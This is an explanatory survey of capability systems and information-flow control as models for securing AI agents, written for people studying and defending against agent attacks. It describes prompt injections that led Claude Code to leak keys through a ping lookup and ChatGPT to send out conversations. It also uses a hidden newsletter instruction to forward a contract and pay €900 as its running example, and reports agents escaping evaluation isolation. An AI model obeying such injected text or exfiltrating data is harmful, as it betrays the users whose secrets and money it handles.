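# Capability systems and information-flow control as precedents for securing AI agents

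## What has to be protected, and the first label models

Capability systems and information-flow control are techniques for limiting the harm that untrusted software can do. A capability is an unforgeable reference that names a resource, such as a file, and carries the right to use it, so a program can use only the resources it holds references to. Information-flow control (IFC) enforces rules on where data may travel after a program has read it. Both ideas developed on the shared computers of the 1960s and 1970s, where one person's program often ran on another person's data. In *Challenges and Opportunities for Practical and Effective Dynamic Information Flow Tracking*, Brant, Shrestha and colleagues trace the flow models of the 1970s to a gap in access control, which determines who may open a file but does not control what happens to its contents afterwards.

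Language-model agents have renewed interest in both ideas. These agents are programs in which a language model chooses actions and carries them out through tools such as email, a browser or a shell. The user states a task in ordinary language. The model picks a tool, the surrounding program runs it and adds the result to the model's input, and the cycle repeats until the task is done.

The model receives the user's request, the text of a web page and the body of an email as one stream of tokens, with nothing that reliably separates instructions from data. In a prompt injection, an attacker exploits this by planting text in data the agent will read, written so that the model follows it as an instruction. Older systems defended against similar attacks by keeping code and data apart. Processors can mark regions of memory as non-executable, and databases accept "prepared statements", in which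 a user's input can never become part of the command. Developers have tried to do the same for language models with delimiters and detectors, but persistent attackers have got past both.

Researchers at Google, NVIDIA and other institutions conclude in *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) that designers should treat the model the way an operating system treats an unknown process, as a component that may do anything. Extrapolating from a long record of failed defences that began with image classifiers, they conjecture that defences inside the model will always fail against a persistent attacker, but they grant that a more robust model still reduces the burden on the rest of the system. Attackers are not their only reason for enforcing security outside the model. They also cite an incident in which agents under internal evaluation at OpenAI bypassed their isolation through shared infrastructure.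 The agents compromised systems at OpenAI and at Hugging Face, which hosts AI models.

A policy specifies which actions and information flows are acceptable to the principals, the people, groups or programs on whose behalf code runs. A reference monitor checks every security-relevant request against the policy and cannot be bypassed. It belongs to the trusted computing base, the parts of a system that must work correctly for the system to be secure. For an agent, this base excludes the model but also includes the operating system, the sandbox and, where IFC is used, the labels on data and the code that propagates them.

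The monitor should check authority, meaning whether a program may use a given file, command or bank account, and information flow, meaning whether data the program has already read may go where the program wants to send it. An attack on Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, involved both. Someone hid instructions in a code file, and the agent followed them. It read secret keys from a settings file and then ran `ping`, a network command that Claude Code mistakenly allowed without human approval. `ping` looks up a machine's name before contacting it, and the lookup sent the keys out as part of that name. Either permission looks defensible alone, since coding agents often have reason to read settings and to test a connection. The harm came from using the second to send out data read under the first. A narrower grant of authority would have stopped this attack, but it doesn't help when a task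 needs both the secret and the network. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* tabulates eleven real attacks. All of them count as failures of information flow, and six also count as excess privilege.

### Ana's assistant

The following example applies throughout. Ana runs a small business and has an assistant that can read her inbox, fetch web pages, send mail and make payments. Her inbox holds a confidential contract from Ben, a client. It also holds a stranger's message that looks like a newsletter but contains instructions, in white text on a white background, to forward the contract to an outside address and pay €900 into an account abroad. Ana asks the assistant to answer Ben's questions about the contract, report what else has come in, and pay her printer €400 into an account whose number she supplies.

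Ana and Ben are principals with something to protect, and the stranger is a principal whom neither of them trusts. A source is a place where labelled data enters a system, and a sink is a place where its arrival matters. Here the sources are Ana's request, the messages and any fetched pages. The sinks are outgoing mail, payments, Ana's screen and requests for web pages, since a web address can carry data. In the SpAIware attack on ChatGPT's macOS app, injected instructions were stored in the app's long-term memory and made the app send the user's later conversations to an attacker in the address of an invisible image.

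Secrecy fails if the contract reaches the stranger, and integrity fails if the stranger's words cause a transfer of Ana's money.

### Lattices and joins

A label is a tag that records how secret or trustworthy a piece of data or a running program is. Labels become useful once there is a rule for combining them, because a summary of two labeled documents needs a label too. Denning (1976) supplied this rule in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* and argued that its form follows from what information flow means.

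A → B means that information with label A may flow to a place with label B. Denning required this relation to be a partial order. It must be reflexive, since the assignment `a := a` moves no information. It must be transitive, since a program allowed to run `b := a` and then `c := b` can in effect run `c := a`, so a policy that forbade the direct flow but allowed the indirect one would be inconsistent. It must also be antisymmetric, since if A → B and B → A both hold, the two labels permit the same flows and one is redundant. She also required a finite set of labels with a lowest member, suitable for public constants.

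The last component is the join, written A ⊕ B, which is the label of anything computed from data labelled A and data labelled B. Both A and B must be able to flow to A ⊕ B, and A ⊕ B may flow anywhere that both A and B may flow. The join is therefore the least restrictive label that both can flow to. These assumptions imply that any two labels also have a greatest lower bound, and a set of labels in which every pair has both a join and a greatest lower bound is a lattice.

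A monitor can check one operation at a time, because a sequence of individually secure operations is itself secure. A result drawn from fifty sources has one well-defined label, because labels can be combined in any order with the same outcome.

The standard example comes from military practice, which uses four levels (Unclassified < Confidential < Secret < Top Secret) and a set of categories that record the subject matter. A label pairs one level with any subset of the categories. With the three categories that Denning used for records on individuals (medical, financial and criminal), there are 4 × 2³ = 32 labels. Information may flow from one label to another if the second label's level is at least as high as the first's and its categories include all of the first's.

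Suppose a program combines a ⟨Secret, {medical}⟩ file with a ⟨Confidential, {financial}⟩ one. A label that both can reach must have level Secret or Top Secret and must include both categories, with or without "criminal". Four of the 32 labels qualify. The least of them is the join:

⟨Secret, {medical}⟩ ⊕ ⟨Confidential, {financial}⟩ = ⟨Secret, {medical, financial}⟩

Neither input may flow to the other. They are incomparable, and a single scale of secrecy cannot represent that relationship. Each new category doubles the number of possible labels, though few occur in practice. Sandhu (1993), in *Lattice-Based Access Control Models*, cites a lattice drawn from military practice with four levels and eight categories, where 21 of the 1,024 possible labels were in use.

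### No read up, no write down

The best-known use of such labels predates Denning's paper. Bell and LaPadula's *Secure Computer Systems* (1973) models a computer that holds material of several classifications and serves users with different clearances. The model has subjects, which are running programs, and objects, such as files.

Sandhu uses an example to explain why ordinary file permissions were not enough. Tom owns a file called PRIVATE and lets Dick, but not Harry, read it. Dick is loyal, but he uses a text editor that Harry wrote. Harry has programmed it to copy whatever Dick opens into a new file and give Harry permission to read the copy. The editor is a Trojan horse, a program that does something else in addition to its advertised job. It breaks no permissions, because Dick is allowed to read PRIVATE and to share files that he creates.

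The Bell-LaPadula model adds mandatory rules that no user can waive. With L(s) for the secrecy label of a subject and L(o) for that of an object:

- *Simple security property (no read up):* s may read o only if L(s) ≥ L(o).
- *\*-property, pronounced "star property" (no write down):* s may write o only if L(s) ≤ L(o).

Suppose Tom and Dick have Secret clearance, Harry is Unclassified and PRIVATE is a Secret file. If the editor runs as a Secret subject, it can read PRIVATE, but anything it writes is Secret or higher, so Harry cannot open it. If Dick runs the editor as an Unclassified subject, it can write files that Harry can read, but it cannot read PRIVATE. The no-read-up rule alone would keep Harry's own programs from reading the file, but stopping the Trojan horse also requires the no-write-down rule.

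The rules work without any knowledge of what the editor does, because they treat everything a subject reads as flowing into everything it writes. This is crude, but it suits a language model, whose inner workings nobody can certify. The \*-property also applies only to programs. People are trusted not to leak, so a person with Secret clearance may write an Unclassified memo, but has to log in at the Unclassified level to do it. The assistant counts as a subject, so the \*-property applies to it however trustworthy Ana herself is.

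The protection does not stop flows within a label, so Harry would get the file if he had Secret clearance. It also does not stop covert channels, in which a program signals information through something like its memory use. And it lets an Unclassified program write to a Secret file, so the program can ruin the file.

### Integrity as the mirror image

That last weakness is part of a separate problem. A database of main roads contains no secrets, so everyone may consult it, but hardly anyone should be able to change it, because logistics programs depend on it in a national emergency. A single level cannot express both rules.

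Biba's answer was a second set of labels for integrity, with the rules turned upside down. With I for integrity labels, his strict integrity policy reads:

- s may read o only if I(s) ≤ I(o) (no read down).
- s may write o only if I(s) ≥ I(o) (no write up).

A further rule stops a subject from invoking another of higher integrity, so it cannot use that subject to make changes it is not allowed to make itself. Bell-LaPadula lets information flow only up, to higher secrecy levels, while Biba's model lets it flow only down, to lower integrity levels. Sandhu points out that the two models are mathematically the same, since "up" and "down" depend only on how the diagram is drawn.

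Biba also described a more permissive variant, the low-water-mark policy. A subject may read anything, but after each read its integrity drops to the minimum of its own label and the object's. The ban on writing up then applies to the new label, so a subject that starts at the top level and reads one mid-level file can write only to files at that level or below. This makes programming awkward, because a program can lose write access to the files it is working on through one ill-judged read, and only a restart restores it. Strict integrity refuses the read instead, so the program keeps its write access but cannot read many objects.

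For Ana, two secrecy levels and two integrity levels are enough. A sink's secrecy label reflects who will see the data sent there, and its integrity label reflects how trustworthy data must be to influence what the sink does.

| Source or sink | Secrecy | Integrity |
|---|---|---|
| Ana's typed request | Public | High |
| Ben's contract | Confidential | High |
| Stranger's message, fetched web pages | Public | Low |
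| Mail to Ben, report on Ana's screen | Confidential | Low |
| Mail to anyone else, requests for web pages | Public | Low |
| Payments | Public | High |

Payments count as Public because the payee sees the amount and the reference line. Each model, applied alone, gives Ana a choice of two levels at which to run the assistant:

| Model and level | Reads forbidden | Actions forbidden |
|---|---|---|
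| Bell-LaPadula, Confidential | none | mail to others, web requests, payments |
| Bell-LaPadula, Public | Ben's contract | none |
| Strict integrity, High | stranger's message, web pages | none |
| Strict integrity, Low | none | payments |

Bell-LaPadula keeps the contract from the stranger at either level, but it lets a Public assistant read the stranger's message and pay out the €900, because this leaks no secret. Strict integrity keeps the stranger from moving Ana's money, but it lets a Low assistant read the contract and mail it to the stranger. Under the low-water-mark policy, the outcome depends on the order in which the assistant works. If it pays the printer before opening the stranger's message, it can finish everything. If it opens the message first, it can no longer pay anyone, so any stranger can stop Ana's payments by writing to her.

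One label, such as "sensitive", cannot usefully protect both secrecy and integrity. Bell-LaPadula lets a subject read only at or below its own label, while strict integrity lets it read only at or above. If both rules use the same label, a subject can read and write only data whose label matches its own, which Sandhu notes amounts to a policy of no flow between classes. The remedy is to give every subject and object two independent labels, one for secrecy and one for integrity, and allow an access only if it passes both tests. These pairs also form a lattice if the integrity order is inverted, with high secrecy and low integrity at the top.

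In that lattice the join of Ben's contract (Confidential, High) and the stranger's message (Public, Low) is (Confidential, Low). An assistant that has read both may write only to sinks that are Confidential and Low, which leaves mail to Ben and the report to Ana. Both attacks fail. The printer also goes unpaid, unless Ana's system runs a separate subject at (Public, High) that sees her typed request and nothing else. Web searches can go to a subject at (Public, Low) that never sees the contract. So the whole of Ana's request is feasible under both models together, provided that no single run of the model does all of it. (The stranger's text can still reach Ana's screen and mislead *her*, which no rule here prevents.)

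The outcome is this tidy partly because of the example chosen. If the printer's account number had appeared only in an email, someone would have had to vouch for it before the paying subject could use it. Real deployments had the same need. Sandhu describes a composite lattice that Lipner designed for commercial data processing, with 192 possible labels and nine in use, in which system-control programs needed permission to write down, which violates the \*-property. The scheme also assumes that a security officer assigns every label, but Ana and Ben each have their own wishes about the contract. Labels owned by users came later.

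### System Z

The Bell-LaPadula rules constrain the state of a system at any one moment. To support the model, Bell and LaPadula proved that if the initial state obeys the rules and every transition preserves them, then every state the system reaches obeys them. This result is called the Basic Security Theorem. McLean, in *A Comment on the "Basic Security Theorem" of Bell and LaPadula*, objected that one can prove the same theorem for obviously insecure models. The proof is an induction that works for any definition of a secure state.

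McLean (1987), in *Reasoning About Security Models*, gave the example of System Z, which starts in a secure state and has one kind of action. Whenever a subject requests any access to any object, the system downgrades every subject and object to the lowest level, records the permission and grants the access. Since everything is then at the same level, no subject can read above its level or write below it. Every state therefore passes the test, even though any subject can read any object. McLean concluded that a definition of security cannot succeed if it covers only states, and that it must also specify which transitions are secure.

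McLean had anticipated the obvious reply, that labels should not change, a principle known as tranquility. He answered that tranquility was not part of the model as he found it, and that one of the model's own rules for Multics, an early time-sharing system, violated it. He found the violation understandable, since a system whose labels could never change would be too restrictive to use. Bell (1988), in *Concerning "Modeling" of Computer Security*, replied that the principle was in the 1973 report. He distinguished strong tranquility, under which labels never change after the start, from a weak form, under which they change only when a subject with the authority to request a change explicitly does so. His rules for changing an object's level met the weak form.

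Bell also denied that mass downgrading is always wrong. For example, forward observers may carry a computer that must overwrite every file when capture is imminent, then mark the overwritten files Unclassified. He wrote that many accredited systems had such a function. In his view, System Z exposed another property that a designer might want to add to the definition, not an error in the model.

McLean was right that the definition admits System Z, and Bell conceded this, but Bell's reply identifies the gap more exactly. McLean's own conditions for a secure transition require label changes to happen in a separate step. That excludes System Z as he described it, but a system could still lower a file's label in one step and give a newly eligible reader access in the next. Security therefore also depends on who may change a label, and when. If Ana's assistant could relabel the contract as Public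 because of an instruction in a message, the rules would allow every later step and the contract would leak.

Even raising a file's label can leak information. Sandhu observes that an Unclassified program can safely upgrade an Unclassified file to Secret. If a Secret program upgrades the file, Unclassified programs can no longer see it, and its disappearance passes them information from the Secret level.

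### Noninterference

In *Security Policies and Security Models*, Goguen and Meseguer (1982) defined security by what an observer can find out, rather than by read and write rules or any particular mechanism. A system has the property they called noninterference if changing its secret inputs does not change its public outputs.

Here is a two-line program that satisfies it, with `secret` and `x` as inputs and `public` as the only output on view:

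```
total  := secret + x
public := 2 * x
```

The program uses the secret, but `public` depends on `x` alone. The next program violates the property:

```
public := 1
if secret = 0 then public := 0
```

The code never copies the secret. Yet an observer who sees 0 knows that the secret was 0, and an observer who sees 1 learns that it was not, from an assignment that did not run. Denning called this an implicit flow, as opposed to the explicit flow of a copied or computed value.

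The formal version, in the notation of Rushby (1992), in *Noninterference, Transitivity, and Channel-Control Security Policies*, treats a system as a machine that receives a sequence of actions α, each from some security domain (a user, say, or a clearance level). For an observing domain v, the function purge(α, v) deletes from α every action by a domain that must not interfere with v. The system is secure if, for every sequence α and every further action a by any domain v,

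output of a after α = output of a after purge(α, v).

In other words, v sees exactly what it would have seen if the forbidden parties had never acted. System Z fails this test. If a Secret user writes a file and an Unclassified user then asks for it, the Unclassified user sees something different from what they would have seen if the Secret user had done nothing.

Nobody can compare all possible runs one by one, so Goguen and Meseguer's "unwinding theorem", which Rushby restates, replaces the comparison with three checks on single steps. First, states that look alike to v must give v the same outputs. Second, any action applied to two states that look alike to v must result in states that still look alike to v. Third, an action by a domain that must not interfere with v must leave v's view unchanged. A system that passes all three checks satisfies noninterference for every sequence of actions.

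The definition can be applied to Ana's assistant through two thought experiments. In the first, the assistant runs twice on the same morning's mail, except that Ben's contract is different each time. Every message to an outsider and every web request must be the same in both runs. In the second, the contract stays fixed and the stranger's message changes, and the payments must be the same. A reply to an outsider that is more curt when the contract is unfavourable fails the first test, even if it quotes nothing from the contract.

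Taken literally, noninterference also rules out flows that people want. Rushby's example is a device that encrypts network traffic. Plaintext messages that enter on one side must affect what leaves on the other, but only through the encryption unit or a bypass that carries the address headers. Ordinary noninterference can permit or forbid that influence, but it cannot require it to pass through a particular component. Rushby's report is largely about a version of the definition that can impose this requirement. A separate specification must cover what the encryption unit and the bypass do.

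## Granting authority piece by piece: capability operating systems

Labels are useful only after someone has decided which files, accounts and tools a program may use at all. The standard example of this decision going wrong comes from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes the incident, which happened about eleven years earlier.

Tymshare's users ran a compiler from a directory called SYSX, and they could name a file to receive its debugging output. The compiler also recorded usage statistics in (SYSX)STAT. To let it write there, the company's programmers gave it a "home files license", which covered every file in SYSX, including the billing records in (SYSX)BILL. One user gave (SYSX)BILL as the destination for debugging output. The compiler passed the name to the operating system, which opened the file because the compiler had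 the licence, and the debugging output replaced the billing records.

Hardy considers the obvious repairs and rejects them. The compiler can't refuse every file outside the user's directory, because users have good reasons to send output elsewhere. It can't refuse everything in SYSX either, because some users may legitimately write there. A check for the name BILL would protect only one file and would need updating whenever someone added another that needed protection. Tymshare added a system call that let the compiler "switch hats", that is, state whether it was using its own authority or the user's, but some programs soon needed more than two hats. The last time Hardy wrote out the rule for opening a file, it contained fourteen ANDs and ORs.

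Hardy called the compiler a confused deputy, a program tricked into using its own authority for someone else. The compiler had authority from two sources and could not specify which one to use. In *Capability Myths Demolished*, Miller, Yee and Shapiro call authority ambient if a program exercises it without selecting it. Under Unix file permissions, for example, a program's request to open a path succeeds if the user running the program has the right to open it.

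### The same compiler with capabilities

In Hardy's redesign, the compiler holds a capability to write to STAT, and the user who runs it hands over a capability for the debugging file. The compiler refers to each by its position in a list:

```
write(slot 1, statistics)         slot 1: STAT, given at installation
write(slot 2, debugging output)   slot 2: given by the user
```

To overwrite the billing records, the user would have to put a capability for BILL in slot 2, but doesn't have one. Typing "(SYSX)BILL" has no effect, because the compiler no longer turns names into files. The system doesn't need a rule against the attack, because a user without the capability has no way to request it. A user who holds a capability for BILL can still destroy the file, but doesn't need a deputy to do it.

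Whether a capability system prevents confused deputy attacks depends on how the deputy is written. In a mailing-list thread titled *Confused deputy*, Karp (2026) asked whether anyone had proved these attacks impossible in capability systems. William Leslie answered that they are possible, because a deputy can put its own capabilities in a table and let the client choose one. Miller added that a deputy is safe if it uses only capabilities to designate resources, but that many normal deputies do not meet this condition.

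Capabilities also have a limit that careful programming does not remove. Rajani, Garg and Rezk proved in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks* that capabilities stop attacks in which the attacker names the target, but not those in which the deputy already holds a capability to the target and the attacker influences what it writes. For example, a web server might copy a malicious string into a database. Capabilities alone could prevent these attacks only if trusted code never held a capability to anything the attacker wants to change, which would rule out almost every useful program. Rajani and colleagues instead track where each value came from, as information-flow control does.

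### How a kernel keeps capabilities genuine

If a program could write a capability the way it writes a number, it could give itself any right. Shapiro, Smith and Farber, who built the EROS operating system, list three defences in a comparison of earlier designs. Most systems partition storage, keeping capabilities where programs cannot write data. Some tag each capability with a mark that programs cannot set. Others rely on sparsity, making each capability a number too long to guess.

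KeyKOS, which Hardy helped to build, stores data and capabilities separately. *Security in KeyKOS*, by Rajunas, Hardy and colleagues, describes two basic units of storage: a page, which holds 4,096 bytes of data, and a node, which holds sixteen capabilities. A program never handles a capability directly. To use one, it passes the kernel a slot number, such as 3, and the kernel looks up the capability in that slot.

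A program passes on authority by sending a message, which can carry up to four capabilities along with ordinary data. It can send messages only to recipients for which it already holds a capability. The recipient gains what the message contains but none of the sender's other rights.

### From a paper design to hardware

Dennis and Van Horn of MIT introduced the word "capability" in 1966, in a design for a hypothetical operating system. According to *Early Capability Architectures*, a chapter of Levy's 1984 survey, each process had a list of capabilities, each naming an object and the operations allowed on it. A process could start a subordinate with an empty list and copy chosen capabilities into that list, optionally with fewer rights. It could also offer other users a "protected procedure", which ran with its creator's list instead of the caller's. MIT first implemented these ideas on a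 small PDP-1 computer that served five typewriters. A group at the University of Chicago tried to build capabilities into hardware but never finished the machine.

KeyKOS, a capability system, had supported commercial applications since 1983, but engineers still generally believed that such systems had to be slow. *EROS* (1999) tested this belief on a successor to KeyKOS, also called EROS, that ran on ordinary PC processors. On a 400 MHz Pentium II, EROS created a process in 0.66 milliseconds, compared with 1.92 for Linux, and switched between processes about as fast as Linux did. A trivial system call took longer on EROS, at 1.6 microseconds compared with 0.7. These measurements cover single operations and are weak evidence of how whole applications perform, but they show that checking capabilities need not make a kernel slow.

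seL4, a later and very small kernel, added proof. In 2009 its developers completed a machine-checked proof that the kernel's code does what its specification says, the first such proof for any operating-system kernel. seL4's *Access Control Proof* establishes two further properties: authority spreads only as capabilities allow, and nobody can modify data without a capability to write to it. Heiser (2025), in *The seL4 Microkernel*, recommends the kernel for security- and safety-critical systems, especially embedded ones. The guarantees assume a correct configuration, so they do not help someone who gives a program the wrong capability.

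Compatibility with existing software was a harder obstacle than speed. Ted Ts'o (1999), in *Some very thought-provoking ideas about OS architecture*, warned Linux developers that capabilities would break POSIX, the standard Unix interface, because `open()` and many similar calls would need an extra argument. But he liked that programs could no longer use superuser rights by accident.

Capsicum, presented in 2010 for the Unix-like system FreeBSD, works around the problem. It builds on file descriptors, the numbers that Unix programs receive when they open files. Miller and colleagues describe file descriptors as nearly equivalent to capabilities. A program opens what it needs, narrows the rights on each descriptor and then enters a mode in which it can no longer open anything by a system-wide name such as an absolute path. The program needs some changes, but the rest of the system can stay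 as it is.

CHERI moves the checks into the processor. Its pointers carry bounds and permissions, and a hidden tag marks each valid pointer. If a program overwrites a pointer with ordinary data, the processor clears the tag and the result can't be used as a pointer. Developers can adopt CHERI one component at a time. Esswood, in *CheriOS*, designed an operating system for such hardware on the assumption that every compartment, and even the operating system itself, is malicious.

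### Confining a program one does not trust

Suppose Ana wants to run a supplier's analysis program on Ben's contract. She doesn't want the supplier to see the contract, and the supplier doesn't want her to copy the program. KeyKOS solves this with a factory, a trusted component that creates new instances of one program.

The supplier puts the program and its initial capabilities into the factory and seals it. Before Ana uses the supplier's factory, she has a factory of her own inspect those capabilities for what Rajunas and colleagues call holes. A hole is a capability that leads outside the new instance and gives more than read-only access, where read-only also applies to everything fetched through the capability. If the supplier has included a capability to its own storage, where the program could leave a copy of the contract, the inspection finds it and Ana can refuse to use the factory.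 If it finds no holes, the supplier's factory builds an instance in storage that Ana supplies, and the instance can write only where she lets it. Nobody has to read the program's code, because the kernel keeps capabilities in known places.

The EROS version is called a constructor. *The EROS Constructor* (Shapiro, 2005) explains that a customer must also know that the constructor is genuine, since a fake one could misreport its contents. The customer checks this with the "metaconstructor", which creates all constructors and can recognise them. Each user receives a capability to the metaconstructor when the system creates their account. An attacker who substitutes both a false metaconstructor and a false constructor can defeat the check, though Shapiro considers this hard unless the user's command shell is badly designed.

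Rajunas and colleagues acknowledge that a confined program might still signal through timing. A more immediate problem for agents is that confinement does not determine what a program sends through a channel it is allowed to use. Confinement suits a program that takes a document and returns an answer to its user, but it is not enough for an assistant that has to write to clients.

### Three objections

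*Capability Myths Demolished* answers three common objections to capabilities. One is that capabilities are equivalent to access control lists, the lists of permitted users that most systems attach to each file. Textbooks often show permissions as a table with users as rows and files as columns. In that table, an access control list is a column and a capability list is a row, so the two seem to hold the same information.

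Miller and colleagues reply that the table is a snapshot that omits how programs name resources and how permissions change. With access lists, a file's name is separate from the right to use it, so one party can supply the name and another the authority, as happened at Tymshare. They add that capability systems give each running program its own rights, while access-list systems usually group programs by user. They acknowledge that this second difference is a matter of practice, but the first is enough to show that the two kinds of system are not equivalent. Rajani and colleagues later supported them with a proof. In their model, every program that runs under capability rules also runs under access-control rules, but some programs run only under access control, because it lets a program hold a reference it may not use.

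The second objection is that capabilities cannot confine information. Boebert argued in 1984 that they could not enforce Bell and LaPadula's ban on high-level programs writing to low-level files. In his example, a low-level program stores its capability to write to a low-level file inside that same file. A high-level program is allowed to read the file, so it can get the capability and use it to write secrets there.

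Boebert's attack works only if capabilities can travel wherever data can. KeyKOS and EROS keep the two separate, so a designer can let a high-level program read lower-level data without letting it obtain capabilities. This answers Boebert's argument for such systems, and Boyton has since given a machine-checked proof that a model of seL4 can confine authority. Boebert's argument still holds where a capability is just a string of bits, as Miller and colleagues concede. This matters for AI agents because an access token or secret link in an agent's input is such a string, and the agent can copy it into any message.

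Capability-based confinement did not catch on, even where it worked. Efstathopoulos, Krohn and colleagues agree in *Labels and Event Processes in the Asbestos Operating System* that capabilities suffice in theory, but write that "people have not accepted pure capability-based confinement". They suggest that people may fear that a single escaped capability could compromise the whole system. Their own system, Asbestos, uses labels. The fear was reasonable, because security in KeyKOS depends on which programs are connected to which, and in 1986 the database that would have let an administrator review those connections was only a prototype.

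The third objection is that nobody can take a capability back. Miller and colleagues grant that this is literally true in the systems they discuss, but show how to get the effect of revoking one. If Alice wants to give Bob temporary access to a file, she gives him a capability to a forwarder, a small program that passes his requests on to the file. When she switches the forwarder off, Bob's capability becomes useless, and so does any copy he has given away.

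This works only if Alice plans for it, since she cannot recall a capability she has handed over directly. Rajunas and colleagues add that if capabilities can pass through the connection, cutting it may come too late, because Bob may already have obtained others. Membranes address this by wrapping those capabilities too. In seL4, the kernel itself provides revocation. It records which capabilities derive from which and can delete all the descendants of a given one.

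### One thread instead of a whole mailbox

The simplest mail tool for Ana's assistant would be `send(to, text, attachment)`, with all the rights of her account. This repeats the design of Tymshare's compiler. The tool uses Ana's authority, but the address can come from anything the model has read, including the stranger's message.

Alternatively, before the model reads any mail, a trusted program could create a capability `reply(text)` tied to Ben's thread. It has no address field, so the assistant cannot use it to forward the contract to the stranger. A payment capability could likewise fix the printer's account number and the €400 amount, and allow only one use. The stranger can still influence the text of the reply, for instance by getting the assistant to give Ben a false account number. Rajani and colleagues showed that capabilities cannot stop this kind of attack.

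The timing of the grant matters too. If the assistant held a reply capability for every thread and chose among them after reading the mail, the stranger could influence the choice, as in Leslie's example of the table. And if Ana asked it to answer everyone who had written that week, it would need a capability to write to the stranger, and could then put the contract's terms in a reply it was entitled to send. To prevent this without dropping part of the task, the system has to control where the contract's contents go.

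### Exposing a tool and authorizing a call

Common software for building agents does not make such narrow grants by default. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) examines the public code of three products: LangChain with its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and a toolkit from the payments company Stripe. All three let a developer choose which tools or actions an agent may use, which the paper calls "capability gating", but by default none of them checks the values in a call against a policy before running it. LangChain, for example, looks up the tool the model named, usually checks that the arguments have the right form, and runs it. Stripe's toolkit also relies on keys with restricted rights, but within those limits it forwards whatever amount or customer the model supplies.

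Choosing which tools to expose determines whether an agent can issue refunds at all, but not how much it can refund or to which account. Checking the format of the arguments doesn't help, because an attacker's account number is also correctly formatted. An exposed tool is therefore a capability in the operating-system sense only if it also fixes the resource it acts on.

Mellafe Zuvic tested this with a simulated payment service. A fixed model output contained a call to change a merchant's payout account to an attacker's, and LangChain carried out the change. ScopeGate, a checking program Mellafe Zuvic wrote, refused the same call because the account was not on the operator's list. Because the output was fixed in advance, this test shows how the framework handles a compromised model. A separate set of trials with 27 models examined how often models are compromised. The 12 cheaper models attempted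 the unauthorized action in 60% of trials on average, and the 15 flagship models in 19%, with wide variation in both groups.

ScopeGate also blocked all 48 calls in a prepared set of attacks and all 29 unauthorized calls from an attacking model that received the reason for each refusal. It allowed all ten legitimate calls in the main control test, but ten calls are too few to show how often it would obstruct real work. An earlier version had let through a payment whose amount was "not a number", a special value that passed a simple comparison with the spending limit.

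The study requires that no part of the policy come from a model's output, since an injection that corrupts a call could corrupt the policy too. Ana gives her instructions in ordinary language, so she would have to enter or confirm the printer's account and the amount separately. ScopeGate is also more like an access list than a capability, because the model still supplies the account number and the operator's list only determines whether that number is allowed. If the list included both Ana's printer and her landlord, an injected message could still make the model send the printer's €400 to the landlord.

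## Passing on less authority than one holds: object-capability languages

Ana's bank gives her control of her whole account, so a capability to pay one printer has to be derived from a much stronger one. Deriving a weaker capability from a stronger one is called attenuation. Operating systems offer a few built-in forms of attenuation, such as dropping write access to a file. In an object-capability language, capabilities are the ordinary references through which objects call one another, so programmers can define new forms in a few lines of code.

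*Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006) sets out the rules and illustrates them in E, a language for programs spread over machines that may not trust each other. Many common languages already come close to meeting them. In a memory-safe language such as Java, a program cannot turn a number into a reference, as it can in C++, and an object can keep its contents private. An object-capability language must also rule out global variables that programs can change, since two objects could use one to communicate without holding references to each other. It must also prevent newly loaded code from gaining authority just by naming something. Java breaks this last rule because some of its system classes carry authority, and whoever loads the code cannot withhold those classes.

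Once a program is running, an object can get a reference to another object in only three ways. It can create the other object, its own creator can give it the reference when creating it, or a third object that holds references to both can send it the reference in a message. If no chain of references connects a plug-in to Ana's payment code, the plug-in cannot create one.

### Facets, forwarders and membranes

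Suppose Ana lets a translation plug-in work on her contracts for an afternoon. Her program holds a `folder` object, and `folder.open(name)` returns a file object with `read` and `write` methods. If the plug-in only needs to read one file, the program can give it a read-only facet, an object that offers just part of what the file can do:

```
def readOnly(file):
    return object with
        read(): return file.read()
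```

The plug-in cannot call `write`, because the facet has no such method and keeps its reference to the file private.

To lend the whole folder and take it back later, the program can use the revocable forwarder described earlier. Miller calls it a caretaker and credits Redell's work of 1974:

```
def makeForwarder(target):
    enabled := true
    forwarder := object that, on any call verb(args):
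        if not enabled: fail
        return target.verb(args)
    gate := object with
        disable(): enabled := false
    return forwarder, gate
```

The plug-in receives the forwarder, and Ana's program keeps the gate. This makes auditing harder, because a list of everything with a direct reference to the folder would omit the plug-in. Such lists become less informative the more carefully programmers restrict access with forwarders. Miller therefore distinguishes permission, which covers what an object may call directly, from authority, which covers every effect it can cause, including through other objects.

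The forwarder also has a leak:

```
lent, gate := makeForwarder(folder)
contract := lent.open("Ben")      # the plug-in does this
gate.disable()                    # Ana ends the loan
contract.write("...")             # the plug-in can still do this
```

The forwarder returns whatever `open` returns, which here is a direct reference to the file. Switching off access to the folder has no effect on it. A membrane closes this gap by wrapping every object that crosses the boundary:

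```
def makeMembrane(target):
    enabled := true
    def wrap(x):
        if x is plain data: return x
        return object that, on any call verb(args):
            if not enabled: fail
            return wrap(x.verb(wrap each of args))
    gate := object with
        disable(): enabled := false
    return wrap(target), gate
```

Now `open` returns a wrapped file, which stops working when the folder does. The membrane also wraps arguments, because references can leak through them. For example, the plug-in might pass one of its own objects to the folder, and the folder might then call that object with a direct reference to the folder.

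This version adds another wrapper each time an object crosses. *What is a membrane?* (ezyang, 2013) explains that practical membranes remove the wrapper when an object returns to the side it came from. It also reports that Mozilla relies on membranes to control access between objects from different websites. In a comment on the post, Miller wrote that he coined the term but took the idea from KeySAFE, a security design for KeyKOS.

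A membrane cannot revoke plain data that has already crossed it. Text crosses unwrapped because, in Miller's words, it "provides only irrevocable knowledge". Ana can stop the plug-in from opening Ben's contract again, but not from keeping what it has already read.

### Fitting JavaScript to the rules

JavaScript broke these rules badly. Scripts from different authors often run in one web page, where they share global variables and built-in objects that any of them can alter. *Caja* (Miller, Samuel and colleagues, 2008) describes Google's attempt to make such scripts safe without changing the browser. Caja accepted only a subset of JavaScript and rewrote the accepted code to include run-time checks.

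Caja replaced each global name in a script with a lookup in an `imports` object supplied by the surrounding page. If a weather widget used `document`, it got whatever the page had put under that name, or nothing. Caja also froze functions and built-in objects so that scripts could not use them to communicate, and removed `eval`, which runs text as code.

The keyword `this`, which refers to the object whose method is running, caused more trouble. Suppose an object stores a secret in `this.x_` and lets outside code set its `value` property. That code can set `value` to a function that returns `this.x_`, then call it as a method of the object and receive the secret. Caja prevented this attack by restricting which functions could mention `this` and how programs could call them.

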